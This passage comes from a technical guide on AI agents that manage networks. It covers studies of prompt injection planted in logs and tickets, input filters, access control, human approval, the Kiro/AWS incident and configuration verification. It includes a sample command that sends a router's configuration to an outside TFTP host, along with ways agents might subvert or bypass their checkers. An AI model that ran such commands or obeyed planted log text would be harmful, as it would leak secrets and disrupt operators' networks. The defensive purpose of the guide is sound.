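| Claude Opus 4.6 | 8.8% | 0.6% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 0% | 0% |

Telling the models not to run fixes protected most of them, but Llama still ran fixes in almost a third of the attacks. Removing the tools that make changes is safer, because the model then cannot run a fix even if it tries to.

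Noticing an attack did not always prevent harm. Claude Sonnet 4.6 detected 72% of the attacks and never ran a planted command, but it ran other dangerous commands in 19% of the trials. It ran none after reading the harmless texts, so the attacks probably had some influence. In another case, Gemini removed a suspicious web address from a planted command and issued the rest, which would have changed a production setting if the test program had not intercepted it.

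Agents can also do damage without an attacker. Llama ran dangerous commands in 44% of its trials with harmless texts, some of which described repairs that staff had already completed. A network agent could likewise read about last month's repair in an old ticket and repeat it.

Pasquini and colleagues tested agents that used GPT-4o and GPT-4.1 and could take up to 35 steps. The agents recommended or carried out the attacker's fix in 90% of 180 trials. Ten standard prompt-injection phrases, which openly tell a model to change its task, failed every time in the setting that had been easiest to attack. Testing an agent only with such phrases would therefore make it look safer than it is.

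### Filters on incoming text

Shah ran the 32 attacks through three filters that scan text for prompt injections before a model reads it. Microsoft's caught one, Google's caught none, and an open-source filter caught one but also flagged a harmless text. All three detected the same instructions when they appeared without the surrounding log text. The timestamps, service names and error messages apparently made the attacks look like ordinary operational text.

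An attacker can also split an instruction across several log entries, so that a filter that checks one entry at a time never checks the whole instruction. *Context Contamination in LLM Analysis of Network Security Logs* (Karanjai, Lu and colleagues, 2026) reports that this succeeded 76.4% of the time in tests. Combining input filters, stricter prompts and checks on the model's output cut the success rate of attacks by about 90%, but 8.4% still worked.

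Pasquini and colleagues had more success with a method that doesn't try to recognise attacks:

1. Before the agent goes into service, a program sends a harmless marker word through every input it can find, such as login forms and web addresses.
2. The program searches the logs for the marker, which identifies the fields that outsiders can write.
3. While the agent is working, software replaces the contents of those fields with labels such as "User#12" before the model sees them.

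The same username always gets the same label, so an agent can still see that one user has failed to log in 500 times. The defence stopped every attack in the tests, and the agents performed about as well as before. But it protects only the fields that the preparation step finds, and the tests used web applications with predictable log formats. It would also be hard to apply to tickets, because the free text is often the only description of the fault.

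### When the agent only writes a report

A policy gate prevents unapproved changes, but an attacker may only want the agent to produce a misleading report. Pandey and Bhujang tested this risk in May 2026 with GPT-4o mini, a small model. They gave it no tools and asked it to classify log entries, summarise them and recommend a response.

Without defences, false claims of authority made the model label 68% of the malicious entries as harmless. When the model wrote summaries, text that imitated the end of the log and a final verdict led it in 96% of cases to leave out the attack, play it down or conclude that no action was needed. The model almost never used the word "benign", so a monitor searching for it would have missed nearly all of these failures.

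Averaged over all tasks and types of attack, the success rate was 26.6% without defences and 11.8% with the best defence. These averages include types of attack that rarely or never worked, so they understate the danger from an attacker who picks an effective method. Giving an agent a read-only login, as Graf advises beginners, doesn't solve this problem, because engineers may still act on its reports.

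### What small models and single steps leave unknown

The models tested in NetInjectBench have only 7 or 8 billion parameters, and none of these studies tested the strongest models available in December 2026. The prompt-based defences might work much better with those. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (2026) describes a public competition in which 464 people made 272,000 attempts to attack agents built on 13 leading models. Success rates ranged from 0.5% for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro. The competition also produced 95 attacks that worked on a Qwen model but on none of the closed models, so results from one model may not apply to another.

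Even a 0.5% success rate matters when an attacker can write to a log with little effort. If each attempt had an independent 0.5% chance of success, 139 attempts would give the attacker a better than even chance of succeeding at least once. Real attempts are not independent, but a public router can easily receive 139 failed logins in a day.

NetInjectBench also stops after one action, whereas a real agent may fetch a log safely and then find the planted text in it. The gate would still refuse an unapproved change at any later step, but it is less clear what an attacker could achieve through a series of permitted actions. For example, an agent might copy a false diagnosis into a ticket, and a second agent might trust it because it came from another agent. Infosecurity Magazine's *“Ghostjacking” Exploits AI Agents’ Trusted Access to Evade Firewall Controls* (2026) describes a similar attack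 that Tenet demonstrated with the error-tracking service Sentry. Sentry's own agent read a fake error report and adopted its fix, and a coding agent that trusted Sentry's agent then ran the attacker's code.

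## Limiting what the agent can reach and change

The policy gate in NetInjectBench refused every unapproved change, but a gate protects a router only if the agent has no other way to log in. Operators therefore restrict the agent's account on the devices themselves. A command may have to pass four checks before it takes effect: the agent's tool list, the gate, the login and the device's own authorisation. A record of the command helps engineers find out who sent it. These limits matter outside networking too. Amazon blamed misconfigured access controls when a cloud service failed in December 2025 after engineers had let an AI agent make changes.

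### One command and four checks

Payments are slow, and an operator asks an agent to find out why. The agent logs in to R4, the data centre's Cisco router, and proposes this command:

```
R4# clear ip ospf process
```

Restarting OSPF on R4 leaves the configuration unchanged, but R4 drops R2 and R3 as neighbours, and the payment servers lose contact with the bank until the routers become neighbours again. Nakamura and Eguchi give a similar example of unacceptable behaviour, in which a model responds to a report of a slow network by offering to reboot the routers on the path.

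| Check | Where it runs | Why it might refuse the command |
|---|---|---|
| Tool list | The program around the model | The agent has no tool that sends free-text commands |
| Policy gate | Between the model and the tools | Nobody has approved this command on R4 |
| Login | R4 | The agent's credentials have expired |
| Command authorisation | R4 and a central server | The agent's account may run only `show` commands |

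The simplest way to limit an agent is to restrict its tools. The ShowNet chatbot had two ticket tools, one to list tickets and one to read them, so it could not edit a ticket even if told to. Its device tool was much broader. The researchers had turned off configuration changes, but the tool still accepted any operational command, including disruptive ones such as `clear ip ospf process`.

The tool list and the gate cover only commands that pass through the operator's software. An agent that can also run a shell on the same machine might find the file with the routers' login details and open an SSH session directly. The login and the command authorisation would still apply, because R4 enforces them on every session. Bilal and colleagues want gates that an agent cannot bypass. An operator can get closer to this by keeping the login details on a separate machine that runs the gate, and by having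 the devices accept the agent's account only from that machine.

### Why shared accounts hide who did what

Many automation tools log in to every device with one service account, which belongs to a piece of software and not to a person. If five engineers, two scripts and an agent all use the account `netops`, R4's log might contain this line:

```
22:10:04  netops  192.0.2.15  clear ip ospf process
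```

When an agent shares an account with engineers and scripts, nobody can tell from the log whether an engineer or the agent sent a command. That slows recovery from an outage, as it did at Rogers, where technicians had to work out which of the night's changes to reverse. The operator also cannot revoke the agent's access without locking out the engineers and scripts. And a shared account needs every permission that any of its users needs, so an agent that only reads logs may get the rights of a script that upgrades software.

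Giving each agent its own account solves most of these problems. The log should also name the person who set the task. At ShowNet, 105 engineers used the same chatbot, so a log that named only the chatbot would not have shown which engineer had set a task.

### SSH certificates that expire

An ordinary SSH key works until somebody removes it from every device. An SSH certificate is a key with conditions attached, signed by a certification authority, a service that the devices trust. Miller (2026), in *SSH Certificate Format*, sets out the conditions in a draft standard. For the job on R4, a certificate might contain these:

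| Field | Example | Effect |
|---|---|---|
| Identifier | diag-agent, task 5521, for M. Sato | Gives the logs a readable name |
| Principal | r4-readonly | R4 decides which account this name opens |
| Validity | 22:00 to 22:30 | R4 refuses logins outside this period |
| Source address | 192.0.2.15 | R4 refuses logins from any other machine |
| Permission to forward ports | Left out | The agent cannot tunnel through R4 to other machines |

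The certificate can also force R4 to run one fixed command, whatever the agent asks for. If a device does not support a restriction such as the source address, it must reject the whole certificate, which is safer than ignoring the restriction.

The short validity matters because the draft defines no way to revoke a certificate, although it advises software makers to provide one. If an agent pastes its private key into a ticket, a 30-minute certificate limits the damage. But the format allows certificates that never expire. The device checks the time only at login, so a session that starts at 22:29 can continue after the certificate expires at 22:30 unless other software closes it.

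Certificates also make the certification authority a valuable target, since anyone who can get it to sign a request can create a login for any device that trusts it. An agent may request a certificate, but the authority should set its terms. Engineers also need a second way to log in, because their own certificates could expire during an outage that cuts them off from the authority. Miller's list of programs that support certificates includes OpenSSH and PuTTY but no router operating systems. The list isn't meant to be complete, so an operator has to check each device. If a device doesn't support certificates, a login server in front of it can check them instead.

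### Asking a server about every command

With TACACS+, a protocol for managing access to network equipment, a device asks a central server who may log in and what they may do. The IETF, the internet's standards body, describes two common ways to authorise commands. A device can ask once per session and receive, for example, a privilege level from 0 to 15. Each level includes everything below it, so the operator cannot pick out individual commands for an agent. Alternatively, the device can ask about each command as it arrives:

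```
R4 asks:         user=diag-agent  cmd=clear  cmd-arg=ip
                 cmd-arg=ospf  cmd-arg=process
Server answers:  FAIL
```

R4 then refuses the command, and OSPF keeps running.

The server receives little context, though. Cisco's `shutdown` command doesn't name a port, so the request R4 sends to the server doesn't name one either. To protect the link to R2, the server has to reject the earlier command that selects that link.

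With TACACS+, an operator can also have the device report every command to a server, along with the account name and the address it came from. The server must store each report before confirming it. The older form of the protocol protects this traffic very weakly, so an attacker between the device and the server can alter the records or change the server's answers. The specification also warns that attackers might plant log entries that make other systems misbehave, which is now a fair description of prompt injection. *Terminal Access Controller Access-Control System Plus (TACACS+) over TLS 1.3* (Dahm, Heasley and colleagues, 2025) replaces the weak protection with the encryption that secure websites use. The standard is only a year old, so many devices in service probably don't support it yet.

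The operator must also choose what a device does when it cannot reach the server. If it permits every command, an agent that accidentally breaks the path to the server also removes its own limits. If it refuses every command, the engineers may be unable to repair the path. A local emergency account whose password the agent cannot read avoids both problems.

### Access control for NETCONF and RESTCONF

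Structured requests need different rules because they do not arrive as typed commands. Bierman and Bjorklund (2018), in *Network Configuration Access Control Model*, define a standard set for NETCONF and RESTCONF. The operator puts accounts into groups and writes an ordered list of rules for each group, and the device applies the first rule that matches. A rule can cover a whole data model, one operation, one kind of notification, or a single setting.

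Suppose the only rule for the agent's group lets it set `enabled` on R4's spare port, eth3. With the standard's default settings, R4 would treat the agent's requests like this:

| Request | Result |
|---|---|
| Read the settings of eth0 | Permitted, because the default allows most reading |
| Switch off eth3 with PATCH | Permitted by the rule |
| Switch off eth0 with PATCH | Refused, because the default denies edits |
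| Replace eth3 with PUT, leaving out its description and IP address | Refused, because this would delete two settings |
| Run a vendor's restart operation | Permitted, unless the vendor has marked it as sensitive |

The defaults deny edits but permit most operations, so an account with no right to edit may still be able to restart the router. An operator can prevent this by permitting the few operations the agent needs and adding a final rule that denies all others.

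The standard also limits what an agent can commit from a shared candidate configuration. At each commit, the device checks the account's rights to every setting that would change. If a colleague has left an unfinished BGP edit in the candidate and the agent has no right to edit BGP, the device refuses the agent's commit.

These rules have limits too. They control which settings an account can change but not which values it can choose, so an agent with permission to change an OSPF cost could raise it from 10 to 100 or to 65,535. A policy gate can check the value. An edit can also change other settings as a side effect, even if the agent has no permission to change them directly. The rules also do not apply to the command line, so an agent with a narrow NETCONF account and a powerful command-line account can do everything the command-line account allows.

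### Permitting listed commands or forbidding listed ones

A deny-list blocks only the commands on it. If R4's deny-list contains `reload` and `erase` but nobody thought to add `clear ip ospf process`, the agent can still restart OSPF. Juniper's example blocklist has the same kind of gap. An allow-list permits only the commands on it, so an agent limited to eight `show` commands could not restart OSPF, even if nobody had foreseen the attempt.

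Deny-lists also go out of date. Bierman and Bjorklund warn that a device can gain new operations that existing rules may not cover. Deny-lists can also miss abbreviations. Cisco routers accept shortened commands, so `relo` restarts a router just as `reload` does, and a gate that searches the agent's text for "reload" would miss it. These gaps matter more with an agent than with most engineers, because an agent that is refused a command may try another way to get the same result, such as switching the interfaces off and on again.

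An allow-list can be too broad as well. Permitting everything that starts with `show` looks harmless, but many Cisco routers accept this:

```
R4# show running-config | redirect tftp://203.0.113.9/r4.txt
```

The command sends R4's whole configuration to another machine. The list should therefore contain complete commands with their permitted arguments, and the gate should refuse `|` except in forms the operator has checked.

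The main drawback of an allow-list is that an unfamiliar fault may need a command that isn't on it. The agent can then ask an engineer to run the command or add it to the list. A sudden rise in refusals may mean that an agent is confused or following a planted instruction. Devices that follow the NETCONF standard count the operations and edits they refuse.

### What a read-only account can still do

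A router's configuration usually contains secrets, such as the OSPF key, the key for the TACACS+ server and users' passwords, some of which are easy to decode. When an agent runs `show running-config`, this text goes to the model, which may run on another company's servers, and it may stay in the agent's logs. A planted instruction could then make the agent copy a key into a ticket that outsiders can read.

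Access rules on a device do not protect copies of its configuration and logs stored elsewhere. ShowNet's chatbot could search the configuration files of 166 devices from the previous year's network, so any password left in those files would have been available to all its users. The IETF notes that some vendors' devices send passwords and encryption keys to the TACACS+ log, and an agent might read that log during an investigation. It is safer to have software replace secrets with labels before any text reaches the model.

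Hiding data on the device can mislead an agent. Under the NETCONF standard, a device omits settings that the agent's account may not read and reports no error. An agent that finds no OSPF key on router R4 might conclude that none is configured and propose a new one, which would break a working connection. The operator should tell the agent which settings it cannot see.

Read-only commands also use the device's resources. Some Cisco `debug` commands don't change the configuration but can produce so much output that the router stops responding. `show tech-support` runs dozens of commands at once, and an agent that suspects a widespread fault may run it on every router at the same time. Many Cisco routers accept only five remote sessions by default, so an agent that opens a new session for each question without closing the old ones can keep engineers from logging in.

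An account with no right to edit the configuration may still be able to lock it through NETCONF and block everyone else's changes, so Bierman and Bjorklund suggest restricting who can use the lock. The gate can cap the number of open sessions and the number of commands per minute, for each device and across the network.

### What a person must see before approving a change

Some changes are too risky for fixed rules alone, so the gate holds them until a person approves. For the OSPF cost change on R1, the request might look like this:

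```
Change 118    diag-agent, for M. Sato, tonight 22:00 to 23:00
Devices       R1 only
Difference    protocols ospf area 0 interface ge-0/0/1.0
              -  metric 10
              +  metric 100
Way back      restore R1's previous configuration over SSH
              (the login path from the offices stays the same)
```

Software should generate the diff between the draft and the running configuration. A summary written by the model can't replace this diff, because planted text can influence what the model writes. The Junos MCP server's commit tool creates no draft to compare, so the approver sees only the lines the model proposes to load.

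The list of devices a change will affect must come from the system that will carry it out, because a single policy edit sent to a controller may change 1,000 routers. The rollback method must still work after the change has gone wrong, so it cannot depend on logging in if the change could block logins.

An approval should apply to exactly what the approver saw. If the agent alters a line, or somebody else changes R1 in the meantime, the gate should require a new approval. A job that spans several devices needs one approval for all its steps. Otherwise an absent approver can leave the job half done, as with the OSPF key that reached only two of four routers.

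Even when a request is perfect, the approver still has to work out what the change would affect. For example, nothing in the request above indicates that the offices' web traffic would take a detour past the data centre.

### How approval becomes routine

If an agent proposes 50 changes a day and a careful check takes six minutes, checking them all would take five hours. At the lowest error rate in NetConfArena, about one faulty submission in 23, roughly two of the 50 would be wrong. Many approvers would start to skim, and the agent's good record would seem to justify it. Something similar happened at Rogers, where the risk rating fell after earlier successes.

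A tired approver may also use the blanket approval that VS Code offers and stop seeing individual changes at all.

Asking for approval less often probably helps most. The gate can automatically allow reads and a short list of harmless changes, such as edits to interface descriptions, so that approval requests are unusual enough to deserve attention. Older network automation divided the work similarly. According to the survey by Zhang and colleagues, controllers acted within set limits while people supervised higher-impact actions.

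An operator can also check whether approval still works by occasionally submitting deliberately faulty changes, which the gate will block even if they are approved, and counting how many the approvers catch. If they catch three out of ten, the approval step offers much less protection than it appears to. The gate should refuse any request that nobody answers.

### The Kiro incident at AWS

The best-known dispute over an agent's permissions involved a cloud service rather than a router, and the agent was Kiro, a coding agent made by Amazon Web Services (AWS). Four people familiar with the matter told the Financial Times, whose account GeekWire summarises, that AWS engineers let Kiro make changes to a system in mid-December 2025. They said the agent chose to "delete and recreate the environment", and the interruption that followed lasted 13 hours. A senior AWS employee told the newspaper that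 engineers had let the agent resolve issues without human intervention, and called the outages "small but entirely foreseeable".

In a public reply, Amazon blamed "user error—specifically misconfigured access controls—not AI". It said that the event affected only Cost Explorer, a service for tracking cloud spending, in one of its 39 regions, and that no customers had inquired about it. It argued that the same misconfigured role could have caused the problem with any developer tool or a manual action. CRN's *AWS Outage Was ‘Not AI’ Caused Via Kiro Coding Tool, Amazon Confirms* reports that, according to Amazon, Kiro asks for authorisation before every action by default and users configure what it may do.

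The two accounts differ mainly over who was at fault. A person with the same role could have deleted the same system, as Amazon says, but an engineer might well have hesitated to delete a live system in order to repair it. An overly broad role may therefore be more dangerous when given to an agent. A narrower role would have blocked the deletion whoever requested it. Kiro requests authorisation by default, but this didn't prevent the outage, and it is unclear from either account whether somebody had switched the request off or had approved the action.

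The Financial Times also reported a second incident, but Amazon called that report "entirely false" in its statement. A spokesperson later told GeekWire that the event had happened elsewhere in Amazon, outside AWS. Fortune (2026) reported in March that internal Amazon documents had originally listed "Gen-AI assisted changes" as a factor in a "trend of incidents", and that the reference to AI disappeared before the meeting about those incidents. Amazon said that only one of them involved AI and that AI had not caused it.

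Staff may also have felt pressure to use the tool. Engadget's *13-hour AWS outage reportedly caused by Amazon's own AI tools* reports that Amazon's leadership had set a goal of 80% weekly use and tracked adoption closely. After the December outage, Amazon made peer review mandatory for production access. A colleague who reviews the access once, rather than every action, is less likely to approve it out of habit, but the agent can still do anything the access allows.

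## Checking a change by computing its effects

An approver who reads a one-line change to a router usually can't tell what it will do to traffic elsewhere. Configuration analysis software can often work this out from the configuration files without touching a device. Alibaba has checked planned changes to its global network this way since 2018, and says that misconfiguration now causes 5% of its network incidents, down from 56%. A harmful change can still pass because nobody wrote down the property it breaks, or because the software's model of a router is wrong.

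### From configuration files to packets

The best-known open tool is Batfish. Brown, Fogel and colleagues (2023), in *Lessons from the evolution of the Batfish configuration analysis tool*, describe four stages:

1. Batfish reads every device's configuration file and translates it into a common model. A Cisco line and a Juniper line that both set an OSPF cost of 500 become the same kind of entry.
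2. It computes the routes. Simulated routers exchange OSPF and BGP routes until no routing table changes any more. The operator supplies what the files leave out, such as which links are up and which routes other organisations announce.
3. From the resulting routes and the access lists, it works out which packets can get from where to where.
4. It compares the answer with a property the operator wants. If the property fails, Batfish returns a counterexample, which is a specific packet that goes wrong, along with the routes and rules it meets on its way.

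A ping tests one packet, whereas the third stage covers every possible packet by working with sets. Let P(x) be the set of packets that can reach point x, and L(x, y) the set that routes and access lists allow to pass from x to y. Batfish starts with all the packets of interest at the source and repeats this step for every connection until nothing changes:

```
P(y) = P(y) ∪ ( P(x) ∩ L(x, y) )
```

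Batfish stores each set of packets as a compact logical formula over the bits of the packet header, without listing packets one by one. On a laptop, it can analyse a real network of 2,735 devices and nearly 16 million routes, and run 100 queries on it, in about five minutes.

One engineer used Batfish to test a change in how a network connected to its provider. The engineer expected to edit two border routers but found, after several rounds of testing, that ten devices needed changes. *A General Approach to Network Configuration Analysis*, the paper that introduced Batfish, reports many violations in two large university networks, and the operators confirmed that most were errors.

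### One changed line on R2

Suppose the company's data centre has divided its addresses, 198.51.100.0/24, into quarters:

| Addresses | Servers | Should outsiders reach them? |
|---|---|---|
| 198.51.100.0/26 | Payment servers | Yes, the bank |
| 198.51.100.64/26 | New customer portal | Yes, from today |
| 198.51.100.128/26 | Backup servers | No |

The last quarter is empty. The internet provider delivers traffic to a quarter only if R2 announces a route for it, and a filter on R2 lists the routes R2 may announce. The firewall permits web traffic to the whole data centre, so only the missing route prevents outsiders from reaching the backup servers.

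An operator asks an agent to put the portal online. The agent's draft changes one line of the filter, shown here in Cisco's syntax:

```
  ip prefix-list TO-PROVIDER seq 5  permit 192.0.2.0/24
- ip prefix-list TO-PROVIDER seq 10 permit 198.51.100.0/26
+ ip prefix-list TO-PROVIDER seq 10 permit 198.51.100.64/26
```

The agent overwrote a line when it should have added one. To see the effect, the company analyses the network twice, with the current files and with the draft. Batfish's differential reachability query does this by comparing the paths of all possible packets in the two versions. The company doesn't have the provider's configuration, so it adds a simple stand-in router that forwards only to addresses R2 has announced. Without the stand-in, the analysis would start with packets that had already arrived at R2 and would show no problem.

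In the current network, L(provider, R2) contains packets for the offices and the payment servers. In the draft, it contains packets for the offices and the portal. The comparison looks like this:

| Web traffic | Now | With the draft | Difference |
|---|---|---|---|
| Internet to customer portal | Dropped | Delivered | Gained, as intended |
| Bank to payment servers | Delivered | Dropped | Lost |
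| Payment servers to bank | Delivered, and replies return | Delivered, but replies are lost | Connections fail |
| Internet to backup servers | Dropped | Dropped | None |
| Offices to payment servers | Delivered | Delivered | None |
| Offices to internet | Delivered, and replies return | Delivered, and replies return | None |

R2 would accept the draft, and a test of the portal would succeed. An agent that ran only that test would report the job done even though the company could no longer take payments.

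### Writing invariants

The comparison lists what changes, but an operator has to say which changes are acceptable. The repair benchmark by Protogeros and colleagues uses four kinds of invariant:

| Kind | Example |
|---|---|
| Reachability | The bank can reach the payment servers |
| Isolation | No outside machine can reach the backup servers |
| Waypointing | Traffic from the internet to the data centre passes through the firewall |
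| Load balancing | Traffic between two sites uses both links |

An operator who uses agents should also require that the offices can open SSH sessions to every router. An access list missing its SSH rule would fail this check before it could lock anyone out.

Invariants are hard to state precisely in English. Brown and colleagues point out that "set A of hosts should reach set B of hosts" has at least four meanings, depending on whether it refers to all or some of the hosts on each side. Exhaustive checks also find violations that don't matter, such as a firewall dropping packets with forged source addresses.

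Software can derive invariants from a working network. In the benchmark, it derived an average of 12,700 per network and as many as 598,000. This avoids a lot of writing by hand, but if the backup servers are already exposed by mistake, the software will record their exposure as an invariant to preserve.

A missing invariant is more dangerous than a badly worded one, because the check passes. Suppose the company has written only two, that customers can reach the portal and that the bank can reach the payment servers. The first draft fails the second of these. The agent tries again:

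```
+ ip prefix-list TO-PROVIDER seq 10 permit 198.51.100.0/24 ge 26
```

This line permits every route inside the data centre's block with a prefix length of 26 or more. Both invariants now hold, so the draft passes, and R2 announces the backup servers to the internet.

A rule that nothing else may change would catch this. Yuan, Ye and colleagues (2025), in *New Evolution of Hoyan*, describe a small language that Alibaba designed for such rules. Here it would take one line:

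```
prefix ≠ 198.51.100.64/26  ⇒  PRE = POST
```

PRE and POST are the routes on all routers before and after the change, so the line requires every route except the portal's to stay the same. The first draft fails because the provider loses the route to the payment servers, and the second fails because the provider gains a route to the backups. A draft that adds a separate line for the portal passes.

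At Alibaba, an operator correctly specified what a change should do but left out the rule "others do not change". The change passed the check, altered other routes, and had to be rolled back. Alibaba now adds the rule by default in some cases.

A check of reachability invariants alone would also have passed the OSPF cost change on R1, because the offices' web traffic still arrives after its detour past the data centre. The check has to compare paths to catch the detour.

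### The propose-and-check loop

An agent can use the checker while it works. It drafts a change, the checker tests the draft on a copy of the configuration, and a failed invariant comes back as a counterexample. For the first draft on R2, the agent might receive this:

```
Violated:  the bank can reach the payment servers
Packet:    203.0.113.5 to 198.51.100.10, TCP port 443
Result:    dropped at the provider, no route
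Before:    delivered, using the route R2 announced
```

The agent revises the draft and tries again until it passes or uses up its attempts, at which point a person takes over.

In *What do LLMs need to Synthesize Correct Router Configurations?*, Mondal, Tang and colleagues (2023) tried an early version of this with GPT-4. They pasted the checkers' messages into ChatGPT by hand because they had no API access to the model. Translating one Cisco configuration into Juniper's format took about 20 messages that software could generate and two that a person had to write. For a routing policy across seven routers, the counts were 12 and two.

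GPT-4 often repaired one error and introduced another. When the researchers gave it a packet that violated a rule for the whole network, it switched back and forth between wrong strategies, so they gave it a separate rule for each router. Some counterexamples still didn't help. GPT-4 wrote a filter that blocked only routes carrying all four labels, when it should have blocked routes carrying any of them. Batfish returned a route that carried one label and got through the filter, but GPT-4 could not fix the filter until a person explained how.

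The loop's success also depends on which errors the checker detects. In *An LLM-based Agentic Framework for Accessible Network Control* (2025), a syntax checker helped GPT-4o correct 87.5% of its syntax errors within five rounds, but with that checker alone, none of the configurations were correct. Accuracy rose to 77% when the system also gave the model a plain-English description of the relevant parts of the network.

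In the more recent experiment by Asadli and colleagues, feedback from Batfish made GPT-5 mini more cautious, but it improved both scores for Qwen3.5-9B, a small model. Qwen's share of regressions fell from 5.6% to 2.9%, and its fix score rose from 18.6% to 20.0%. GPT-5 mini did best when it received all the files at the start instead of having to look for them, with a fix score of 49.1% and regressions of 1.3%.

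These results probably overstate the benefit of the feedback, since the checker tested exactly the properties that the researchers used for scoring. A real operator's invariants would be less complete. But the checker could detect all the remaining regressions. The experiment scored the agent's final draft regardless, whereas an operator's gate could refuse any draft with a known violation and leave the network unchanged.

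### What Alibaba's checks caught

The longest public record comes from Hoyan, Alibaba's own analysis system. The company's network has more than 2,000 routers, and Hoyan handles on the order of a hundred change checks a week, most of them from automation. According to Yuan and colleagues, it prevents on the order of ten incidents a year. These are the causes of the risks it found in 2024:

| Cause | Share |
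|---|---|
| Wrong commands | 37.5% |
| Flaws in the design of the change | 34.4% |
| Existing misconfiguration that the change would have triggered | 15.6% |
| Failed links or other topology problems | 6.3% |
| Other | 6.2% |

The shares are consistent with a total of 32 cases. The mistakes in the commands included mistyped router names, wrong address blocks and the use of another vendor's format. An agent could also make all of these mistakes.

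In one case, an engineer wanted to move traffic for a list of IPv6 destinations from one internet provider to another. Hoyan confirmed that the listed destinations would move, but it also predicted overloaded links to the new provider. The engineer then added a check that other routes would not change, and that check failed. The change used the command `ip-prefix` instead of `ipv6-prefix`. That vendor's routers compare only IPv4 addresses with an `ip-prefix` list and let all IPv6 routes through, so every IPv6 destination would have moved.

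In another case, the plan was correct, but the existing configuration had a flaw. Two routers should have had the same routing policy, but one lacked a rule. This did no harm while a different rule hid the gap, but engineers planned to delete that rule. Traffic would then have taken a roundabout path and overloaded a link. A reviewer who read only the planned commands would have been unlikely to notice the problem.

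Misconfiguration's share of all network incidents fell from 56% to 5%, but growth in other kinds of incident would also lower that share. The figures are also the company's own. Yuan and colleagues attribute the remaining 5% to settings that Hoyan doesn't cover, such as maximum packet sizes.

### Features and bugs outside the model

Few operators have Alibaba's resources. *Towards Accessible Model-Free Verification* (Krentsel, Ye et al., 2025) surveyed 30 network engineers. Among those who knew of verification tools, 74% named missing support for their protocols or features as a barrier. The Google researchers also tried Batfish on 1,500 production router configurations, and it could not parse any of them.

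A partial failure is more worrying because the tool still returns a result. In a smaller test with configurations of 62 to 82 lines, Batfish did not recognise about 40 lines in each. Some of these lines controlled things like status lights, but others switched on MPLS, which affects how routers forward traffic. A gate should refuse a draft if the checker can't read a line that might matter.

The model can also misinterpret lines that it parses. Krentsel and colleagues connected three Arista routers in a row, and Batfish reported that one of them could not reach its neighbour, although it could when running the real software. Batfish had ignored an interface's address because the address came before another command in the file. This was a false alarm, but the same kind of mistake could hide a real fault.

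Brown and colleagues found that most of Batfish's modelling errors come from undocumented device behaviour, such as what a router does when its configuration refers to a filter that doesn't exist. They find these errors by comparing Batfish with real device software every day, and argue that an imperfect tool can still catch serious errors.

AI may make the models easier to extend. In *Self-evolving network verifiers* (Protogeros, Schneider and Vanbever, 2026), coding agents based on Claude Opus 4.8 and Sonnet 5 added three missing routing features to a small verifier. After each attempt, software compared the verifier's routes with those from a reference system and returned every disagreement to the agent. Each feature cost between $19 and $42, and all the final versions passed every test, though this proves agreement only on the tested cases. For two of the features the reference was Batfish,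 so the agents would have copied any mistakes in it.

A model of correct behaviour won't predict bugs in a vendor's software, so finding them requires running the real software. In one outage that Krentsel and colleagues describe, a router sent an unusual but valid BGP message, and another vendor's routing software crashed while parsing it.

### Timing, load and stale data

Configuration analysis normally computes the routes a network settles on, but some networks can settle on more than one set of routes. If two border routers each prefer routes learned from the other, the result can depend on which one receives a route first. Batfish computes one result, which may not be the one the real network reaches. The analysis also doesn't show how long the network takes to settle. Krentsel and colleagues describe a case in which mismatched timers on two vendors' routers slowed recovery from a cut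 link and caused tens of minutes of severe congestion.

A reachability check also passes a change that sends all traffic over one low-capacity link. Hoyan predicts load by simulating billions of measured traffic flows, which takes ten servers a few minutes. The prediction depends on accurate measurements. When Alibaba investigated errors in Hoyan's results over six months, more than half came from problems in its monitoring data, such as missing routes, an outdated map of the network or wrong traffic volumes. *The Case for Validating Inputs in Software-Defined WANs* (2024) finds that incorrect inputs to network controllers played a part in over a third of a large cloud provider's major outages over five years.

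The analysis can also miss the states between the old configuration and the new one. On R4, both the old access list and the finished new one were fine, but a state in between caused the lockout. Bilal and colleagues describe avoiding such temporary violations as the real challenge in deploying a change.

An operator can also check the intermediate configurations if the order of the steps is fixed. A change made to n devices one at a time passes through n + 1 configurations, including the first and last. If the devices can change in any order, there are up to 2ⁿ possible configurations, or 1,024 for ten routers. For the OSPF key change on four routers, a tool that models the keys would detect the split after the second router changes, but not the brief loops that form while routers recompute their paths.

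### Keeping the checker out of the agent's reach

An agent should be able to run the checker and read its results, but not to change what it checks or skip the final run. Otherwise a planted instruction, or just a persistent attempt to finish the task, could lead the agent to delete the invariant that blocks its draft. It could also get a harmless draft approved and send the router a different one. The policy gate can prevent this by running the final check itself:

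1. The gate fetches the running configurations from the devices, so the agent can't supply outdated or altered copies.
2. It applies the agent's draft to those copies and runs the checker with invariants that only engineers can edit.
3. It refuses the draft if an invariant fails, if the checker can't read a relevant line, or if the checker crashes or runs out of time.
4. It confirms that nobody has changed the devices in the meantime, and then sends them exactly the text it checked.

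The gate needs its own tests, because a bug can let a bad command through, as one did in Facebook's audit tool. Engineers can test it with deliberately faulty drafts, as they would test human approvers.

Some invariants can also stay hidden from the agent until the final check. An agent that sees every invariant may satisfy the wording of one in a harmful way. For example, it could keep outsiders away from the backup servers by removing the servers' route from the whole network, which would also cut off the offices. In their experiments with EvidenceNet, Zhang and colleagues gave the agents no access to the evaluator or its checks of the final network.

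Coding agents that extend a verifier also need to be separate from the agents that propose changes. An agent that did both could make a failing change pass by editing the verifier's model.

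## Rehearsing changes in emulated networks and laboratories

Configuration analysis predicts a change's effects from a model of each router, and the model can be wrong. In a rehearsal, the agent first makes the change on a test network, often one that runs the router makers' own software. This can reveal faults that the model misses, such as a command that behaves differently on one maker's routers, and it shows how the agent reacts to surprises. But no test network is a complete copy of the production network. Swisscom, Switzerland's largest telecoms company, had an outage after a change that had passed its laboratory tests.

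### Four kinds of test network

A simulator, such as Batfish, models how a network behaves without running any device software. According to Microsoft's *Advancing global network reliability through intelligent software part 1 of 2*, the company uses another simulator to check, for example, whether it can safely take a link out of service for the next two hours. The simulator uses the live state of the network and the expected traffic, and no change can go ahead unless it passes the simulator's checks.

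An emulated network runs device software in virtual machines, which each have their own operating system, or in containers, which share the server's operating system and usually start faster and need less memory. NetConfArena used the open-source program GNS3 to run vendors' router software. ANI-Gamut used Containerlab, which builds a network from a text file. Part of a file for the four-router network might look like this:

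```
topology:
  nodes:
    R1:
      kind: juniper_vjunosrouter
      startup-config: R1.cfg
    R4:
      kind: cisco_iol
      startup-config: R4.cfg
  links:
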